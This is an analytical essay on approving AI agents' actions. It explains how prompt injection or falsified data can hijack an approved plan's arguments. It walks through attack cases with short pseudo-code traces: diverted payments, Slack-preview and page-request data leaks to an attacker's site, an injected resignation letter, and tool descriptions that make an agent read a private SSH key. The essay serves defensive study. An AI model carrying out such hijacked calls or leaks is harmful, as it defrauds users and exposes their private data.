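# What approval of an AI agent's actions should cover when attackers can shape the message, the payee or the file

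## What does a person approve when they approve an agent's plan?

An AI agent is a language model that uses software tools to act, for example to send an email, pay a bill or move a file. Agents make mistakes and outsiders can mislead them, so most commercial agents ask a person for permission at certain points. *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent–Human Interaction Problem* (Wang, Li and Tian, 2026) surveyed 21 agent products as of April 2026 and found that 15 make such requests. OpenAI's *Understanding prompt injections* describes agents that ask before they send an email or complete a purchase, and advises users to review the details before approving. The protection an approval gives depends on exactly what the person has permitted, but agents often ask before they have worked out everything they will send, pay or move.

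A tool call is a request from an agent to a tool. It consists of the tool's name and its arguments, which are the values the agent gives the tool. Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026), part of the specification of a common standard for connecting models to tools, gives the example of a call named "get_weather" with one argument, the location New York. The name determines the type of action, such as looking up the weather or sending an email, and the arguments determine all the details. The specification recommends, but does not require, that a person always be able to refuse a call and that the software show the user the arguments before sending the call. A plan is the list of tool calls an agent intends to make. Some arguments may be blank until the agent looks something up.

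The agent often looks up untrusted data, meaning anything it reads that someone other than the user could have written, such as incoming mail, a web page or a supplier's invoice. Prompt injection is text in such data that makes the agent do what the text's author wants instead of what the user asked. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, written for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre in December 2025, David C describes a recruiter who uses a model to score CVs. A candidate hides an instruction in the CV to approve it, and the model may follow it. The model receives the recruiter's instruction and the CV as one run of text and predicts what comes next, with no enforced boundary between the two. Databases long had a similar weakness, which programmers could fix by keeping commands and data apart. David C thinks there may never be such a fix for language models,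 and advises builders to limit what a misled model can do.

### The schedule email

Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues (2025), in *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, give an example small enough to take apart. An assistant can read and write a user's email and calendar. The user asks it to "send today's schedule to my boss", John Doe. Before it opens the calendar, the assistant draws up a plan of two calls:

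```
calendar.read(today)
email.write(____, "john.doe@company.com")
```

The user's request fixed both tools, their order, the day and the person who gets the email. The assistant had to supply John's address, which is harmless if it came from a contact list only the user can edit. Only the body of the email was left blank, and the assistant writes it from the calendar entries after the first call returns. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues call this design plan-then-execute, because the agent fixes its tool calls before it reads any untrusted data. They point out that an instruction in a calendar entry cannot add a third call but could change the body of the email in any way.

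Other people write much of a user's calendar, even though it feels like the user's own document. Google's *Manage invitations in Calendar* lists three settings. Under the loosest, every invitation sent to the user's own address goes onto the calendar automatically. The middle setting does this only for senders who are in the user's contacts, belong to the same organisation or have dealt with the user before. Under the strictest, an event appears only after the user has responded to the invitation by email. Brown University changed its default from the loosest setting to the middle one after a rise in fake invitations (Grossi, 2026, *Google Calendaring with Outside Collaborators*). That should keep most strangers out, but a colleague, or someone who has broken into a colleague's account, can still put text on the calendar without the user doing anything. The user also wants some of that text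 in the email, because a schedule without other people's invitations would be incomplete.

Some arguments set a destination, which is where something goes, such as John's address here or a bank account in a payment. Others set the content the agent sends or writes, which here is the email's body. Others set an amount, though the schedule email has none. Others set a selection, which is the record or file the agent uses. Here the selection is "today", and the user made it.

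Other requests leave different details for the agent to fill in. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues also consider an assistant asked to find all tax-related PDF files and move them into a folder called Taxes. The user has named the destination, but the agent chooses which files to move by looking through files that an attacker may have written. They concede that even in a tightly restricted version of that assistant, a malicious file could end up in the wrong place. In another example, a user wants to tell "my regular collaborators" about a vacation. The user supplies the gist of the message, and the agent infers the recipients from recent meetings and emails, which other people helped create.

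### Four things a person can approve

The broadest approval covers a type of action, such as sending email. Products usually offer it as an "always allow" button, which Wang and colleagues found to be the most common way of sparing users repeated questions. Pressing it approves not only the email that prompted the question but also emails that have not been written yet. If the user had pressed it last month, the assistant could send today's schedule email to any recipient with any body, and could send any number of emails, all without asking.

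A plan settles much more. Someone who approves the two lines above has agreed that the assistant will read one day's calendar and send one email, to John. They have not seen the email, because the assistant has not written it yet, and they do not know which calendar entries it will read, since an invitation may arrive after they approve the plan. According to Wang and colleagues, the coding agent Devin handles this kind of gap by asking for approval twice, first of the plan and then of the resulting code changes.

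The person can also wait until the blank is filled and approve one complete tool call, with John's address and, say, four lines of appointments. Every argument is then filled in, but the four lines may still be inaccurate, and the person may not have read them, which depends partly on the software. Wang and colleagues report that ChatGPT's Actions feature and the agent Manus, in its default mode, ask for a yes or no with almost no information about the action, whereas Claude Code prints the raw command. A user who says yes after seeing only "Allow this action?" has formally approved a complete call, but in practice has approved little more than a type of action. The software also has to tie the approval to those exact values, which security engineers call binding, so that the approval lapses if any of them changes before the email goes out.

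Products usually ask people to approve complete calls, which is tiring because one coding task can produce dozens of requests. To reduce that burden, an agent can instead ask about a piece of data. In *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026) use the term endorsement for a person's decision to treat some untrusted data as trusted. Their agent, Prudentia, labels everything it handles as trusted or untrusted, and anything it derives from a mixture of the two is labelled untrusted. Once untrusted text has entered the planning model's context, consequential calls generally need a person's approval. Kolluri and colleagues give the example of a harmless email listing ten tasks, each requiring such a call. The user can approve ten calls, or endorse the email once and let the agent proceed.

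Suppose an assistant of this kind asked the user to endorse today's calendar entries. The user would know what the entries say and would have decided to rely on them. The endorsement would not settle how the assistant words the email, and it might leave more than that open, because Prudentia can make further consequential calls without asking after an endorsement. If the user overlooked an instruction in one of the entries, the endorsement would cover that instruction too. The user would make one decision instead of ten, and everything the ten would have covered would depend on it.

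Kolluri and colleagues chose not to offer the equivalent shortcut for secrets, which would let the user declare private data fit to share. They argue that whether data is fit to share depends too much on the situation, and that approving the individual call captures this better. I think most people would agree in the case of the schedule email, because a user who would happily send a doctor's appointment to a spouse may want to keep it from a boss.

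Wang and colleagues examined 21 products and found that none lets users label data as trusted. They suspect this is because people readily judge whether an action is risky but do not naturally think of data as trusted or untrusted. They do not think the effort of labeling fully explains the absence, because researchers have published labeling methods that require little work from users.

Some coding agents now have "auto modes" that ask the person for approval less often by giving the decision to a second language model. *Explicit authorization scope improves LLM-based permission checking in coding agents* (2026) describes a checker that compares each proposed call with the user's request and either allows or blocks it. The request is then the only thing the person has approved, so its wording matters a great deal. In the paper's example, the checker lets an agent delete artifacts that belong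 to another user, but blocks the same deletion once the request includes a restriction on ownership.

### Two attacks, written as pairs

Gong and Deng (2026), in *PlanGuard*, a paper on a defence for agents, write every action as a pair, (tool, arguments), and use the notation to separate two attacks. In function hijacking the agent calls a tool that nobody asked for, with arguments the attacker chose. In argument hijacking it calls the tool the user wanted, again with the attacker's arguments:

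```
function hijacking:  (t_adv, v_adv)
argument hijacking:  (t_correct, v_adv)
```

An adversary ("adv") can change which tool an agent calls ("t") or the values of the tool's arguments ("v"). In function hijacking, the agent calls the wrong tool, as when a user asks for a summary of an email and the agent sends one instead. If the user asks the agent to delete a temporary folder and it deletes a system folder, the tool is right but the argument is wrong.

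*Invitation Is All You Need!* (2025) reports a demonstration of function hijacking on a real calendar. The researchers sent an invitation to a user of Google's Gemini assistant, and when the user asked to hear the week's events, the assistant deleted one. As a pair, that action is (delete event, an event from the user's calendar). The two-line plan for the schedule email includes no deletion, so an assistant that kept to the plan could not have deleted the event.

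Argument hijacking of the schedule email looks different:

```
(email.write, [attacker's text, "john.doe@company.com"])
```

An attacker can change the contents of a message while the tool and the address still match the plan. *Securing LLM Agents Need Intent-to-Execution Integrity* (Qu, Xu and colleagues, 2026) describes an example in which a user asks an agent to debug an application and email a report to a teammate. An instruction in a log file changes the body of the report so that it includes secret settings from the user's machine, which the user did not ask to send.

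The boundary is less clear when the attacker gets the assistant to send a second email, to a stranger. This is argument hijacking under Gong and Deng's pairs, because the request does call for the email tool. Qu and colleagues instead test whether the user intended the call, and the user intended only one email, so the second fails the test. The label matters little to someone approving a plan, because the plan lists one email and a second would depart from it. Other papers use different names for much the same division. *SOK* (2026) uses the term "argument injection", and *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) separates control flow (which calls run, in what order and under what conditions) from the data that shapes their arguments.

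Gong and Deng assume that the attacker plants an instruction. Girrens and Wang (2026) point out in *SPA* that this isn't necessary. In their example, a user asks an agent to pay an invoice that lists the attacker's bank account. The agent takes the account number from the invoice, as anyone would, and sends the money to the attacker. Argument hijacking can therefore happen without prompt injection, through data that contains no instruction.

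That makes it harder to say when an argument counts as hijacked. A colleague's meeting title is also text that someone else chose, but it belongs in the schedule email. Gong and Deng's test is whether the arguments conflict with the user's constraints or intent. The test is easy to apply to the email's destination, because the user named John. It is harder to apply to the body, because the user said only "today's schedule", and a false appointment can fit that description as well as a real one.

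## How can a plan run as approved and still do harm?

The blank in the schedule email's plan is an example of a general problem that Girrens and Wang describe. A plan has to commit to tool calls before their results exist, and those results may become the arguments of other calls. Developers could require exact arguments from the start, but Choi, Kim and colleagues (2026) warn in *Agent Data Injection Attacks are Realistic Threats to AI Agents* that the agent would then lose the flexibility to adapt to what it finds. Exact matching also causes false alarms. Gong and Deng tested it with a 2025 model by comparing every call with a plan drawn up from the user's request alone. The comparison wrongly flagged 27% of harmless cases in one half of their test and 38% in the other, often because the agent had written the same value differently.

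Fixing only the calls still gives a good deal of protection. *Architecting Resilient LLM Agents* (Del Rosario, Krawiecka and Schroeder de Witt, 2025) compares plan-then-execute with a common kind of agent that chooses each step after reading the result of the last. Suppose such an agent opens a web page containing an instruction to send the user's chat history to a stranger. It reads the instruction before choosing its next step, and may obey. If the agent had fixed its plan beforehand, the instruction could not add a step to it.

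In their example of the harm that remains, the agent searches the web for the latest company report, then emails a summary to the CEO. In this trace and the ones below, capitals mark what an attacker can choose.

```
web.search("latest company report")
email.send(SUMMARY OF THE ATTACKER'S PAGE, ceo)
```

The attacker controls the website and has put malicious content into the report. The agent follows its plan correctly and delivers that content to the CEO, possibly as a phishing message, which tricks its reader into giving something away. Del Rosario and colleagues also recommend giving an agent only the tool its current step needs, so it cannot send an email while adding up costs. That would not protect the CEO, because the attack takes effect at the step where the agent has to send an email.

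### What four designs leave to the attacker

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues describe several designs that keep untrusted data away from an agent's decisions. In one of these, plan-then-execute, an attacker can change only the body of the email when an assistant sends someone a schedule. The attacker can still make the assistant leave out a meeting, invent one, add a request or a link, or replace the schedule with something else.

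Other requests need a looser plan. For the vacation notice, the plan must contain something like "for each regular collaborator, send the notice". A person who approves this plan approves a loop, and an attacker may be able to influence how many times it runs and who gets the emails.

The map-reduce design gives each piece of untrusted data to a separate model and then combines the answers. In the paper's example, a user wants the agent to find this month's invoices and email the information to the accounting department.

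```
for each file:
    LLM("is this an invoice?", file)      -> YES or NO
email.write(information from the files marked yes, accounting)
```

A malicious file can get itself marked as an invoice, but it cannot change how any other file is marked. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues point out that the attacker could have achieved as much by supplying an actual invoice. But a convincing invoice can still do harm if it has the wrong bank account on it. The protection also depends on what reaches the model that writes the email. If the model receives only the yes-or-no answers, and ordinary software attaches the files, no instruction in a file can reach it. If it reads the files to summarise them, one malicious file could change the email's summaries of all the others.

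In the dual LLM design, a privileged model plans and calls tools but never reads untrusted data. A quarantined model reads the untrusted data but cannot call tools. It can put its answer into a named variable, which the privileged model passes on without looking inside. Ordinary software fills in the value when the call runs. The paper's example is an email address that the agent needs from an untrusted text:

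```
VAR = quarantined_LLM("find the email address", text)
send_email(VAR, message)                  -> goes to THE ATTACKER'S ADDRESS
```

The person who wrote the text cannot give the privileged model instructions, but can choose the address. The privileged model never reads the address, so it cannot notice a wrong one. Anyone who approves these two lines in advance cannot notice it either, because they see only the name of a variable. For the schedule email, the quarantined model would write the body and John's address would come from the user's contacts, so the attacker could influence the text as much as before.

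Code-then-execute takes this further by having the agent write a complete program:

```
entries = calendar.read(today)
body = LLM("format this data", entries)   -> ANY TEXT
email.write(body, "john.doe@company.com")
```

An instruction in a calendar entry can still change the email's text, because the program's middle line passes the entries to a model. The program does show that the entries go into the body and not the address. Other software can use that to check where each argument came from, but the program alone does not stop the email.

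### Routes to harm

The damage an attacker can do depends on which argument they control and on who or what receives the result.

A false destination is the simplest case. Girrens and Wang give a version of their invoice attack that takes two days.

```
Monday:   details = read_invoice("Acme"); save(details)
Tuesday:  pay(THE ATTACKER'S ACCOUNT, details.amount)
```

On Monday the user asks the agent to fetch an invoice from Acme and save the details. On Tuesday the user asks it to pay that invoice. Tuesday's plan is correct, but the account number comes from the agent's notes, so it may look like something the agent already knew even though an outsider supplied it.

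A message can also reach the right person and deceive them. One of the goals that Beurer-Kellner and colleagues attribute to an attacker is to get a colleague of the user to approve a security-sensitive action or ignore an alert. In the schedule email this takes one extra line:

```
email.write(today's appointments + A REQUEST TO APPROVE SOMETHING, john)
```

John has reason to trust the request because it comes from his employee's real account, with an otherwise accurate schedule. The harm happens when he acts on it, after the agent has finished. The paper warns developers not to assume that email within an organisation is safe enough to skip review. Skipping that review might not let data leave the organisation, but it would let this attack through.

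A reply that the user asked for can leak private data. In another request in the paper, the user asks the agent to answer an email with whatever information its sender wants, using the user's recent mail.

```
emails.search(TERMS THE SENDER INFLUENCED)
email.reply(the answer + PRIVATE DATA, sender)
```

Here the destination is correct, but the sender is the attacker. An instruction in the incoming email could make the assistant look for more sensitive information and include it in the reply in a form the user cannot see. The attacker may not need an instruction, because the user told the assistant to supply what the sender requests, and the sender can request something confidential. Qu and colleagues also count it as a violation when the recipient is innocent, as when a debugging report carries secret settings to a teammate, because the data has still crossed a boundary that the system should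 have enforced.

Some requests leave the agent a choice that an attacker can influence. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues describe a booking assistant whose plan is to query hotels, pick the one that best fits the user's criteria and book it.

```
choice = best(hotels, criteria)           -> THE ATTACKER'S HOTEL
book(choice)
```

A separate model with no tools can rate each hotel, but it has to read a description the hotel wrote. If the model reads each description separately, a hotel can't lower another's rating, though it can still inflate its own. The paper reaches the same conclusion about CVs in a hiring assistant.

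Qu and colleagues offer a definition of when such a choice counts as manipulated. Let *J*(*q*, *d*) be the decision an agent reaches on a request *q* after reading data *d*, and let *δ* be added text that does not change the correct answer, such as praise. They require that

*J*(*q*, *d* ⊕ *δ*) = *J*(*q*, *d*),

where *d* ⊕ *δ* is the data with the extra text in it. In other words, flattery should make no difference to which hotel the agent books. The definition is less helpful with lies. A false claim of ten years' experience would mislead a careful person who had only the CV to go on, so an agent could believe it without reasoning badly.

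Wrong selection is also the main danger with files, as for the assistant that gathers tax-related PDFs. The attacker controls the contents or names of one or more files. Under plan-then-execute the assistant commits to two commands, "find" and "mv" (move), and Beurer-Kellner and colleagues show how little that settles:

```
find(SENSITIVE FILES)
mv(SENSITIVE FILES, A PUBLIC NETWORK DRIVE)
```

Both commands are on the approved list, and together they publish the user's private files. If the plan also fixed the Taxes folder as the destination, the files would stay off the public drive. Even a move within the user's own storage can do harm. The attacker's goals that the paper lists for the email assistant include moving important messages to a folder the user rarely checks.

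Content can also act on the recipient's software before anyone reads it. *AI Agents with Formal Security Guarantees* (Balunović, Beurer-Kellner and colleagues, 2024) demonstrated this with a message sent only to the user. The user asks an agent to read a spreadsheet of customer feedback and message them on Slack, the workplace chat program, with a summary of the five most negative comments.

```
feedback = read_sheet(id)
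summary = summarize(feedback)             -> summary + A LINK
send_slack_message(me, summary, preview=True)
```

The attacker had written one of the comments, which made the agent add a link containing the spreadsheet's contents and pointing to the attacker's server. Slack fetches linked pages by default to show a preview, so it sent the data to that server without anyone clicking. Balunović and colleagues reproduced the leak in two widely used agent systems, and the providers then fixed it.

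Someone checking the recipient would have seen only their own name, while the actual destination was inside the content. The preview setting, an argument that seems to affect only display, determined whether the data left without a click.

The recipient may also use an agent. Beurer-Kellner et al. note that a tampered reply could carry further prompt injections to the user's colleagues. If an AI assistant reads John's mail, the schedule email is untrusted data for that assistant, even though John knows the sender.

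Finally, a plan may contain conditions, and an attacker can control which of them are met. In *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too*, Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026) study agents that operate a computer by looking at the screen and clicking. One model writes the whole plan before anything appears on the screen, so the plan has to cover whatever might appear. Another model looks at the screen and answers the questions written into the plan.

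```
if visible("cookie notice"):              -> YES
    click(find("cookie notice"))          -> THE ATTACKER'S ADVERTISEMENT
```

Foerster and colleagues describe an attack, which they call branch steering, in which an advertisement imitates a cookie notice. The model that reads the screen identifies the ad as a cookie notice, so the plan's branch for notices runs, and the click opens the attacker's site. The attack worked in their tests on 2025 models, and asking another model to double-check the screen did not reliably prevent it.

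These plans are also long. For tasks in which an agent calls named tools such as "send email", the measured plans averaged 3.7 branches. For tasks on a computer screen, they averaged 39.7 branches over 213 lines of code, and roughly half of a plan's steps were fallbacks that did not run on a given occasion. Anyone who approves such a plan is approving dozens of steps that will probably not run, some of which an attacker may be able to trigger.

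The attacker is still limited to actions the plan contains. Almost every browsing plan has a branch for cookie notices, so an attacker can easily anticipate it. Foerster and colleagues expect diverting a transfer of funds to be much harder, because the attacker would have to deceive the screen-reading model several times in ways that match one particular plan. Email assistants can also have simple branches. If a user says "accept the invitation if I am free", anyone who can add an appointment to the calendar can influence whether the assistant accepts.

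### Does an attacker gain much once the tools are fixed?

A developer might accept all of this and reply that it leaves the attacker with very little. Evidence for that view comes from AgentDojo, a set of simulated email, chat, travel and banking tasks in which researchers plant instructions for an agent to find. In one defence, a model picks the tools a task needs before the agent starts, and the agent gets no others. *Least-Privilege Auditing of Agent Tool Calls with Intent Graphs and Reasoning-Guided Escalation* (2026), which draws on AgentDojo's published logs, reports that this defence reduced the share of attempted attacks that achieved the attacker's goal from 45.7% to 6.5% on 76 tasks. The agent completed about as many ordinary tasks as before.

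*NOMOS* (2026) reports weaker results for the same defence. The defence let 11.8% of attacks through, and the share of ordinary tasks completed fell from 79.2% to 58.3% because it removed tools that some of those tasks needed. It decides once per task which tools to remove and does not check individual calls, so an attack that needs only the remaining tools can still succeed.

A complete fixed plan seems to do better. When Girrens and Wang tested their planner with its data checks switched off, 4 of 949 attacks (0.4%) succeeded, all against the same user task in banking.

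These results say more about some attacks than others. AgentDojo's usual attacks try to make the agent do a different job from the one the user gave it, which often requires a call that is not in the plan. Choi and colleagues added 108 attacks that leave the user's task alone and falsify the data the agent relies on. They ran both kinds on GPT-5.2, a model from December 2025:

| Design | Planted instructions | Falsified data |
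|---|---|---|
| No added defence | 0.2% | 49.1% |
| Plan-then-execute | at most 0.7% | 40.7% |
| Dual LLM, without rules on data | at most 0.7% | 25.0% |

Plan-then-execute prevented only about a sixth of the successful attacks that used falsified data. The dual LLM design prevented about half, and failed in the other cases because the quarantined model extracted wrong values and the rest of the system used them. Current models may give different rates, but the large difference between the columns is still a reason not to conclude from a low score against planted instructions that an agent's arguments are safe.

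The developer's reply is right when untrusted data can produce only a few values and all of them are acceptable. The file assistant in the design-patterns paper has three tasks, and two of them can meet this condition. To collect tax documents, a separate model can answer yes or no for each file. To sort the Downloads folder, it can choose from a fixed list of categories. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues conclude that in both cases a malicious file can at worst affect what happens to that file. The remaining task is to identify songs through an online service and rename each file with its artist and title. No short list can contain every artist and title, so the new name has to be free text.

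A model limited to a short list of answers can still do harm if one of those answers is dangerous. For example, if the model answers yes or no to "has the manager approved this payment?", a false yes can release the money. An attacker who can supply a hundred files can also try to influence a hundred answers.

A strict format has a similar weakness. Software can require a value to be a well-formed bank account number, which leaves no room for an instruction, but the attacker's account number would also pass this check.

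The schedule email would be almost safe if ordinary software copied the start and end times from the calendar into a fixed template and left out titles and descriptions. Someone who sent the user an invitation could still make John believe the user was busy at ten o'clock, but could not add a request, a link or any private data. John would also not learn what the meetings were, though telling him that may have been why the user wanted to send the schedule.

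Limits on length fall somewhere in between. For a coding agent that reads other people's documentation, Beurer-Kellner and colleagues suggest reducing the documentation to a formal description with method names of at most 30 characters. They think this would probably remove any injected instruction, but it would also remove the explanations and examples that programmers find useful.

A plan can run as approved and still do harm when the user wants the agent to pass on text that someone else wrote. In *The Granularity Mismatch in Agent Security*, Fan, Li and colleagues (2026) give the example of a user who asks an agent to summarise a web page and email the summary to their boss. The page has to influence the body of the email but should not influence who receives it. Fan and colleagues built a monitor that enforces this distinction for each argument of a tool call, but they state that its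 guarantee does not cover harmful text inside a permitted body.

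## What have tests and attacks on agents shown?

The agent in Atlas, OpenAI's web browser, looks at pages, clicks and types much as a person would. OpenAI's *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025) describes how the company searches for prompt injections that work on this agent. OpenAI trained a second language model to write them. This model can try a draft on a simulation of the agent, read a record of the agent's reasoning and actions, and revise the draft several times before settling on a final version.

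One attack it found began with an email in the user's inbox containing an instruction to send a resignation letter to the user's CEO. Later the user asked the agent to draft an out-of-office reply. The agent came across the email while working on this and took the instruction as genuine. It sent the CEO the resignation letter in the user's name and never wrote the out-of-office reply.

```
asked for:   draft(out-of-office reply)
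happened:    send_email(A RESIGNATION LETTER, THE CEO)
```

Whether the attacker added an action here depends on how one describes the agent's tools. If automatic replies and sending email are separate tools, the agent called a tool the user hadn't asked for, which is function hijacking. If one tool handles all outgoing mail, the agent called the right tool with the wrong recipient and body, which is argument hijacking. The Atlas agent works by clicking and typing, which the user wanted it to do. At that level, almost any attack on it changes only the arguments, which are where it clicks and what it types.

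An approval to "send an email" would have let the resignation letter through, and the user might easily have given that approval after asking for help with a message. Showing only the recipient would have helped only a little, because a CEO is an ordinary person to get an out-of-office reply. Showing the body would have revealed the attack, because anyone who asked for an out-of-office message would notice that they were reading a resignation letter.

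OpenAI does not say whether the agent asked for confirmation before it sent the letter, so the case is not evidence about whether a user would have approved the letter after seeing it. It is still good evidence that an attacker could choose what the agent sent and to whom.

The letter would also have been unusually easy to catch, because the attacker replaced the whole message. If the attacker had changed only the address for urgent payments in a normal out-of-office reply, a preview would still have shown the full reply, but the user would have needed to know the correct address to notice the change.

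OpenAI trained a new version of the agent against attacks like this and released it to all Atlas users before publishing the demonstration. It gave no success rate for the attack, and a year later the case doesn't show how well the current agent resists such attacks.

The same post contains a hypothetical attack that is easier to classify. A user asks the agent to summarise unread emails, and a malicious email gets the agent to forward tax documents to the attacker. Summarising does not require sending any mail, so a request for permission to send an email would itself be a warning. In the out-of-office case, the user half expects that request. An added action can therefore be much easier for the user to notice than a changed argument in an action they already expect.

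### When reading a page sends data

OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) describes an attack on ChatGPT's deep research mode, in which the agent reads many sources before it answers. Outside researchers reported the attack to OpenAI in 2025. The user asked the agent to research that day's emails and check every source that could bear on a new employee process. One email, which looked like a routine follow-up about a restructuring, instructed the agent to extract an employee's name and address and submit them to an outside service. It also claimed that the agent was already authorized to do this. The attack worked 50% of the time in testing with that user request. OpenAI does not give the number of trials, and the rate might be quite different for a narrower request.

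The user asked the agent to read, and the attacker made it send the employee's details. This may not require a new type of action, because opening a web page can also send data out, as in the Slack leak that Balunović and colleagues demonstrated. If the agent submits the details that way, the attack needs only one more page request, with an argument the attacker designed. Requesting pages is already the agent's job, and the user's instruction to check every source even seems to cover the extra request.

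```
open_page(a relevant source)
open_page(THE ATTACKER'S SITE + AN EMPLOYEE'S NAME AND ADDRESS)
```

Someone who approves "browse the web" would let this call through, and probably would not think of it as sending anything. The second line shows the problem if the software displays the whole address and the person reads to the end.

OpenAI's safeguard, Safe Url, is designed to detect when information the assistant learned in a conversation is about to go to a third party. It then either shows the user that information and asks for confirmation, or blocks the transmission and tells the agent to find another way. When asked to confirm, the user would see a name and a home address, which a general question about browsing would leave out. OpenAI reports that most of the attacks it sees against ChatGPT try to extract secrets like this, and that the model refuses in most of the cases it knows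 of, so the safeguard is rarely needed. But it only guards against leaks, so it may not stop a resignation letter, which need not contain anything secret.

OpenAI also argues that filters which sort incoming text into malicious and harmless usually miss well-developed attacks of this sort. It says that recognising one is as hard as recognising a lie, often without the context needed. For example, to spot the one bad request among several reasonable ones in a restructuring email, the recipient would need to know whether the company has such a compliance service.

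An attacker can also add an action without writing anything for the model to read. Constantin (2026), in *AI agent security*, reports a flaw that Manifold Security found in Claude for Chrome, Anthropic's browser assistant. The assistant has nine built-in tasks that start when the user clicks, but it did not check that the click came from a person. Another browser extension could therefore start one of the tasks and have the assistant read the user's Gmail, Google Docs and Calendar. Manifold rated the flaw high severity, rising to critical for users who had switched on "Act without asking" mode, in which the assistant reads silently.

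In that case the attacker forged the user's request, so the assistant wrongly believed the user had started the task. Showing the user every recipient and every word of a message would not prevent this. Asking before acting does help, because the user knows they never started the task.

### Tests that count arguments

Most tests of agents record whether the attacker achieved their goal, but not how. Two papers from 2026 examine the arguments passed to the agents' tools.

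Yu, Xing and colleagues (2026), in *Readable Before Actionable*, built a test with six tools: weather, calculator, email, calendar, search and file access. Each prompt combined a harmless request with a tool result that contained an argument from the attacker, such as an instruction to send an email to a different address. The attack succeeded if the model put that argument into its tool call. Qwen-2.5-7B, a small model from 2024, did so in 88.2% of cases. With clean tool results, it supplied the correct argument 92.5% of the time.

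Yu and colleagues then tried changing the model's activations, which are the lists of numbers that one layer of a neural network passes to the next. To find out how to change them, they gave the model identical commands in two roles. "Calculate 24 plus 76" was an instruction when the prompt told the model to execute it, and data when the prompt told the model to summarise a note containing it. They averaged the activations for each role and subtracted the data average from the instruction average. This gave them a direction, *d*, pointing from "data" towards "instruction".

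During the test they edited each activation *h* at one late layer, just before the model chose its next action:

*h* ← *h* − *λ* · max(0, ⟨*h*, *d*⟩ − *μ*) · *d*

The term ⟨*h*, *d*⟩ is how far the activation lies in the "instruction" direction, *μ* is the average for harmless prompts, and *λ* is the strength of the edit. The edit pushes an activation back only if it lies further in that direction than the harmless average. Loosely speaking, this makes the model's state less like that of a model that has just received an instruction.

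With this edit, Qwen used the attacker's argument in 12.4% of cases, down from 88.2%. Its accuracy on clean tool results fell only slightly, from 92.5% to 91.2%. Such a large effect from a small edit suggests that much of the problem, at least in this model, was that it treated data as instructions.

The result has several limits. Only someone with access to a model's internals can make the edit, which rules out most people who use a commercial agent. In a separate test on Llama-3.1-8B, another 2024 model, attackers who adapted to a similar edit succeeded 27.4% of the time, compared with 26.3% without the edit. On Qwen, when the attacker concealed the meaning of the instruction, the edit reduced the success rate only from 74.2% to 62.1%. Making the model less responsive to instructions also would not obviously stop it from copying a false account number from an invoice.

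Dai, Sun and colleagues (2026), in *Subverting Tool Arguments*, tested a different source of bad arguments, and used newer models. Under the Model Context Protocol, whoever supplies a tool also writes a description of it, which explains to the agent when to use the tool and how to fill in its arguments. Dai and colleagues altered only these descriptions. The tools' code and the format of their arguments stayed the same. In their main example, a user asks an agent to read and summarise a project report, and the description gets it to open a different file:

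```
asked for:   read_file(project report)
happened:    read_file(A PRIVATE KEY)
```

The file is an SSH key, which can let its holder log in to other computers. The tool then handles the path it receives as designed.

Dai and colleagues drew 109 tasks from three existing benchmarks, covering 118 tools in areas such as file management, web browsing and finance. They refined each altered description by trying it on an agent with made-up requests, then tested it on three new requests per task. An attack counted only if the agent chose the attacker's tool over harmless alternatives and filled in every value the attacker had picked. It also had to get past five detectors that scan descriptions for signs of tampering. These are the attack success rates on that strict count:

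| Benchmark | Average of six models | GPT-5.6-Luna |
|---|---|---|
| MSB | 93.8% | 100.0% |
| MCP-SafetyBench | 81.5% | 77.8% |
| MCPTox | 63.8% | 62.7% |

The MSB percentages are all multiples of one sixteenth, which suggests that this benchmark contributed only 16 tasks. If so, a single task changes a model's score by about six points. The rates are still very high, including for a 2026 model from a leading company.

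The attacker in this test influences both halves of the pair, since the agent also has to pick the attacker's tool. But the type of action is still the one the user wanted, so a person who approves "read a file" has approved reading the key.

These results are a problem for plan-then-execute, because an agent has to read its tools' descriptions before it can plan. If an outsider wrote those descriptions, the plan may already contain the attacker's value. The person approving the plan can at least see the wrong file path in it, whereas the body of the schedule email was still blank when the user saw that plan.

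The lowest rates come from MCPTox. Dai and colleagues attribute this to the users' requests, which state exact values such as the path of the file to read, while the other two benchmarks leave the agent to work the value out. It is plausible that a description would have more trouble overriding a value the user has given. But their more detailed results for one model, Qwen3.8-27B, make this effect look smaller than the table suggests. Before detection, the attack succeeded in 88.0% of cases on MCPTox, 93.8% on MSB and 100% on MCP-SafetyBench. With the detectors, the MCPTox rate dropped to 72.0% and the other two did not change. On this model, more of the gap came from detectors catching the altered descriptions than from the agent keeping to the values the user had given.

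So a user who names the exact file cannot count on the agent to open it. Naming it still helps, because the user or ordinary software can then compare that name with the agent's call before the call runs.

### The rates in system cards

AI developers publish success rates for prompt injection in system cards, the reports that accompany new models. These rates have fallen a lot in 2026.

According to VentureBeat, Anthropic's February system card for Claude Opus 4.6 reported no successful attacks across 200 attempts in a restricted coding environment. When the model operated a computer through its screen, a single attempt succeeded 17.8% of the time without additional safeguards. *Prompt Injection Robustness*, a summary of results for Anthropic's later Mythos Preview, gives 0.43% for the same kind of test. Without safeguards, attacks in a web browser succeeded against Opus 4.6 in 80.41% of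 cases and against Mythos Preview in 1 of 148.

Claude Opus 5 also did well. The Decoder reports no successful attacks in 129 browser scenarios. On a more general benchmark from the security firm Gray Swan, attackers who had 15 attempts succeeded 2.0% of the time, compared with 5.5% for Opus 4.8, 2.6% for Mythos 5 and 2.8% for Fable 5. In September, Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Opus 5.5 said the model was similar to or better than Opus 5 on every prompt-injection test in the card, but warned that it was more likely than earlier models to follow some malicious instructions.

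OpenAI's figures are similar. TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* covers an August update to the card for GPT-5.6. Attacks placed in material the model read through a tool succeeded 3.77% of the time against Sol, 3.32% against Terra and 2.94% against Luna, the model's three versions. Direct attacks, in which the user tries to override higher-priority instructions, succeeded against Sol about 0.05% of the time, so the agent is evidently more vulnerable to attacks in what it reads. Each company chose its own attacks and environments, so the difference between 2.0% and 3.77% does not show that Anthropic's models are safer than OpenAI's.

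The rates above describe models that are some months old. Newer models have followed, including Claude Fable 5.2, whose card Mowshowitz (2026) reviewed in November in *Fable and Mythos 5.2*.

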